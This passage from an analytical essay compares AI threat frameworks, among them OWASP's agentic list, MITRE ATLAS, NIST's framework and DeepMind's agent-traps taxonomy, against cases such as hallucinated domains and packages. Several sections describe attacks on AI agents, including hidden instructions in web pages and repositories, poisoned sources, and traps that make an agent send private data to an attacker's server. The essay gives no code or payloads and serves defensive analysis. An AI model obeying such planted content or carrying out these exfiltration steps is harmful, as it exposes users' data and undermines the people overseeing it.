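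A narrower rule would be easier to justify. If several models give the same domain name as a bank's login address, even at low temperature, a registry could delay its sale until the buyer shows a connection with the bank. ICANN's contracts don't require this.

### What published comparisons measure

Nguyen and colleagues scored 16 frameworks against their 193 threats in a 2026 paper responding to a NIST request for information. A score of 1 means minimal guidance, 2 means moderate or indirect coverage, and 3 means a direct and specific defence. They counted a threat as covered if the score was 2 or more.

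| Framework | Covered (2 or 3) | Direct and specific (3 only) |
|---|---|---|
| OWASP's agentic list | 65.3% | 14.5% |
| CDAO toolkit (US Defense Department) | 62.2% | 4.7% |
| ATFAA-SHIELD (Amazon Web Services engineers) | 62.2% | 3.1% |
| MITRE ATLAS | 52.8% | 9.8% |

NIST's AI Risk Management Framework scored 48.7%, and the lowest of the 16 frameworks scored 6.2%. The second column matters more for the argument about separation, and ATLAS ranks second there instead of fourth. The figures of 4.7% and 3.1% are each framework's total minus its share of 2s. A framework can earn a 2 for many threats with one broad entry, so the breadth criticized in the second premise raises the headline percentages.

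The abstract says that no framework covers a majority of the threats in any category. That can't be right, because OWASP's agentic list covers 65.3% of all the threats, so it must cover a majority in at least one category. The abstract probably means the weaker claim in a later caption, which is about averages across all 16 frameworks.

The choice of threats also affects the result. An AI model generated them, and a professional with an Nvidia certification in agentic AI reviewed them. The prompts required the model to explain how each threat differed from the risks of single AI systems and from those already in NIST's publications, including AI 100-2. Scoring NIST on threats selected this way puts it at a disadvantage. The results also have little bearing on the six test cases, since a chatbot that gives a customer the wrong bank address is a single system.

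Some of the threats do come close. In one, an attacker changes the API address in an agent's settings, so the agent sends its text to a server posing as a well-known provider's. The server accepts the same requests as the real API and records them. This is much like the scam endpoint, except that the attacker has to get into the settings first. The weakest category across all the frameworks was Non-Determinism, with an average of 1.231. It concerns the unpredictability of models, which is also partly why a watchlist of invented names is never complete.

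*MCP-38* rates coverage of its own subject as partial in both OWASP lists, indirect in ATT&CK and absent from NIST's AI Risk Management Framework. Nguyen and colleagues, by contrast, gave the NIST framework 48.7%, partly because they counted general duties to identify and manage risks as moderate coverage and assessed the framework together with AI 100-2. Those general duties would not give an engineer a specific fix, but they might help a manager decide who should look for one.

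The *Cisco Integrated AI Security and Safety Framework Report* (2025), which introduces Cisco's own framework, criticises ATLAS for relying on documented attacks, leaving gaps on agents and not prescribing controls. The criticism about documented attacks is partly fair, but ATLAS listed hallucinated names long before Unit 42 reported criminals registering hallucinated domains. The criticism about controls is too strong, because ATLAS does list mitigations, though none for checking who owns a domain.

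All these comparisons measure what the documents contain, but none tests whether a team that uses a better-scoring framework stops more attacks. Researchers could test this by giving two groups of analysts the same incident reports and different frameworks, then comparing how often the analysts agreed on a label and chose a defence that worked.

### From content to action

Zhang and colleagues treat generative AI as a continuum from content, where a model writes something that a person reads, to action, where an agent carries out operations. They arrange attacks by how much access the attacker needs, how much the attacked system does by itself, and how far the harm spreads. They call this an "organizing lens" and don't propose new terms or a catalogue.

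The second dimension separates two cases that OWASP's LLM list groups under Misinformation. The hallucinated bank domain is near the content end because a customer reads the address and decides whether to click, while the hallucinated repository is near the other end because the agent downloads it and may run it. The model makes the same kind of mistake in both cases, but a warning beside the link could help only in the first. The attacker doesn't need access to the model or the user in either case, so the other two dimensions don't distinguish them as clearly.

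The scheme can also classify harm from an agent's own actions, which ATLAS can't. But every stage in its diagram of attacks, from direct prompt injection to attacks on several agents, involves an attacker. The scheme also has no numbered entries to file incidents under, so it can't help with counting them.

The paper's second distinction, between security and safety, fits the cases less well. Zhang and colleagues say that security threats are usually met with a technical fix, whereas reducing safety harms relies more on platforms' rules, new laws and cooperation between institutions. No attacker was behind the spread of react-codeshift, which makes it a safety problem, yet Eriksen made the name safe in a day by publishing an empty package. HalluSquatting better supports their broader point about coordination, because it persists partly because the companies that run the models, the agents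 and the platforms each regard it as somebody else's problem.

### Traps for agents

*AI Agent Traps*, by Franklin, Tomašev and three colleagues, all at Google DeepMind, is closer to a taxonomy. It defines a trap as content engineered to misdirect or exploit an AI agent that encounters it, and sorts traps into six classes by what they target: the agent's perception, reasoning, memory and learning, actions, interaction with other agents, or human overseer.

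Franklin and colleagues describe their framework as the first known systematic one for such threats. The Decoder's *Google Deepmind study exposes six traps* quotes Franklin as saying that every type of trap has documented proof-of-concept attacks, but the paper describes the traps involving several agents or a human overseer as more theoretical. The evidence is stronger for hidden instructions in web pages. In one study the paper cites, such instructions in 280 test pages changed models' summaries in 15% to 29% of cases, depending on the model.

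The scheme fits the image link well. Its Data Exfiltration Traps induce an agent to find private data, encode it and send it to an attacker's server, which describes EchoLeak fairly well. ATLAS already treated this case separately, so the scheme adds little here.

The DeepMind framework is more useful for the scam endpoint, because one of its trap types covers false statements planted in the sources an agent retrieves so that the agent treats them as verified fact. This could describe the fake SolanaAPIs documentation if ChatGPT found it by searching. ATLAS splits such pages between two techniques, depending on how the agent reached them. But DeepMind's definition requires a trap to be aimed at an agent, and the thieves may have written their documentation for human programmers. As with data poisoning, an analyst would have to know what the thieves intended.

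A hostile repository is also a trap once the agent has opened it. The framework has no entry for how the agent got there, so the entry for the librepods copy would cover its hidden instructions but not the wrong guess that led the agent to them. The entry would be the same if the agent had followed a correct link to a hostile page, even though looking up the owner would help only when the agent had guessed wrong.

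The remaining three cases are outside the taxonomy's scope. The bank's customer isn't an agent, nobody set a trap with react-codeshift, and nobody misled Claude Haiku 4.5 into writing to the police. One kind of trap does spread in a similar way to react-codeshift. A story about a model's identity circulates online, and the model retrieves and repeats it. An invented package name can circulate the same way without anyone planting it, but the taxonomy's entry for this trap covers only deliberate stories about what a model is like.
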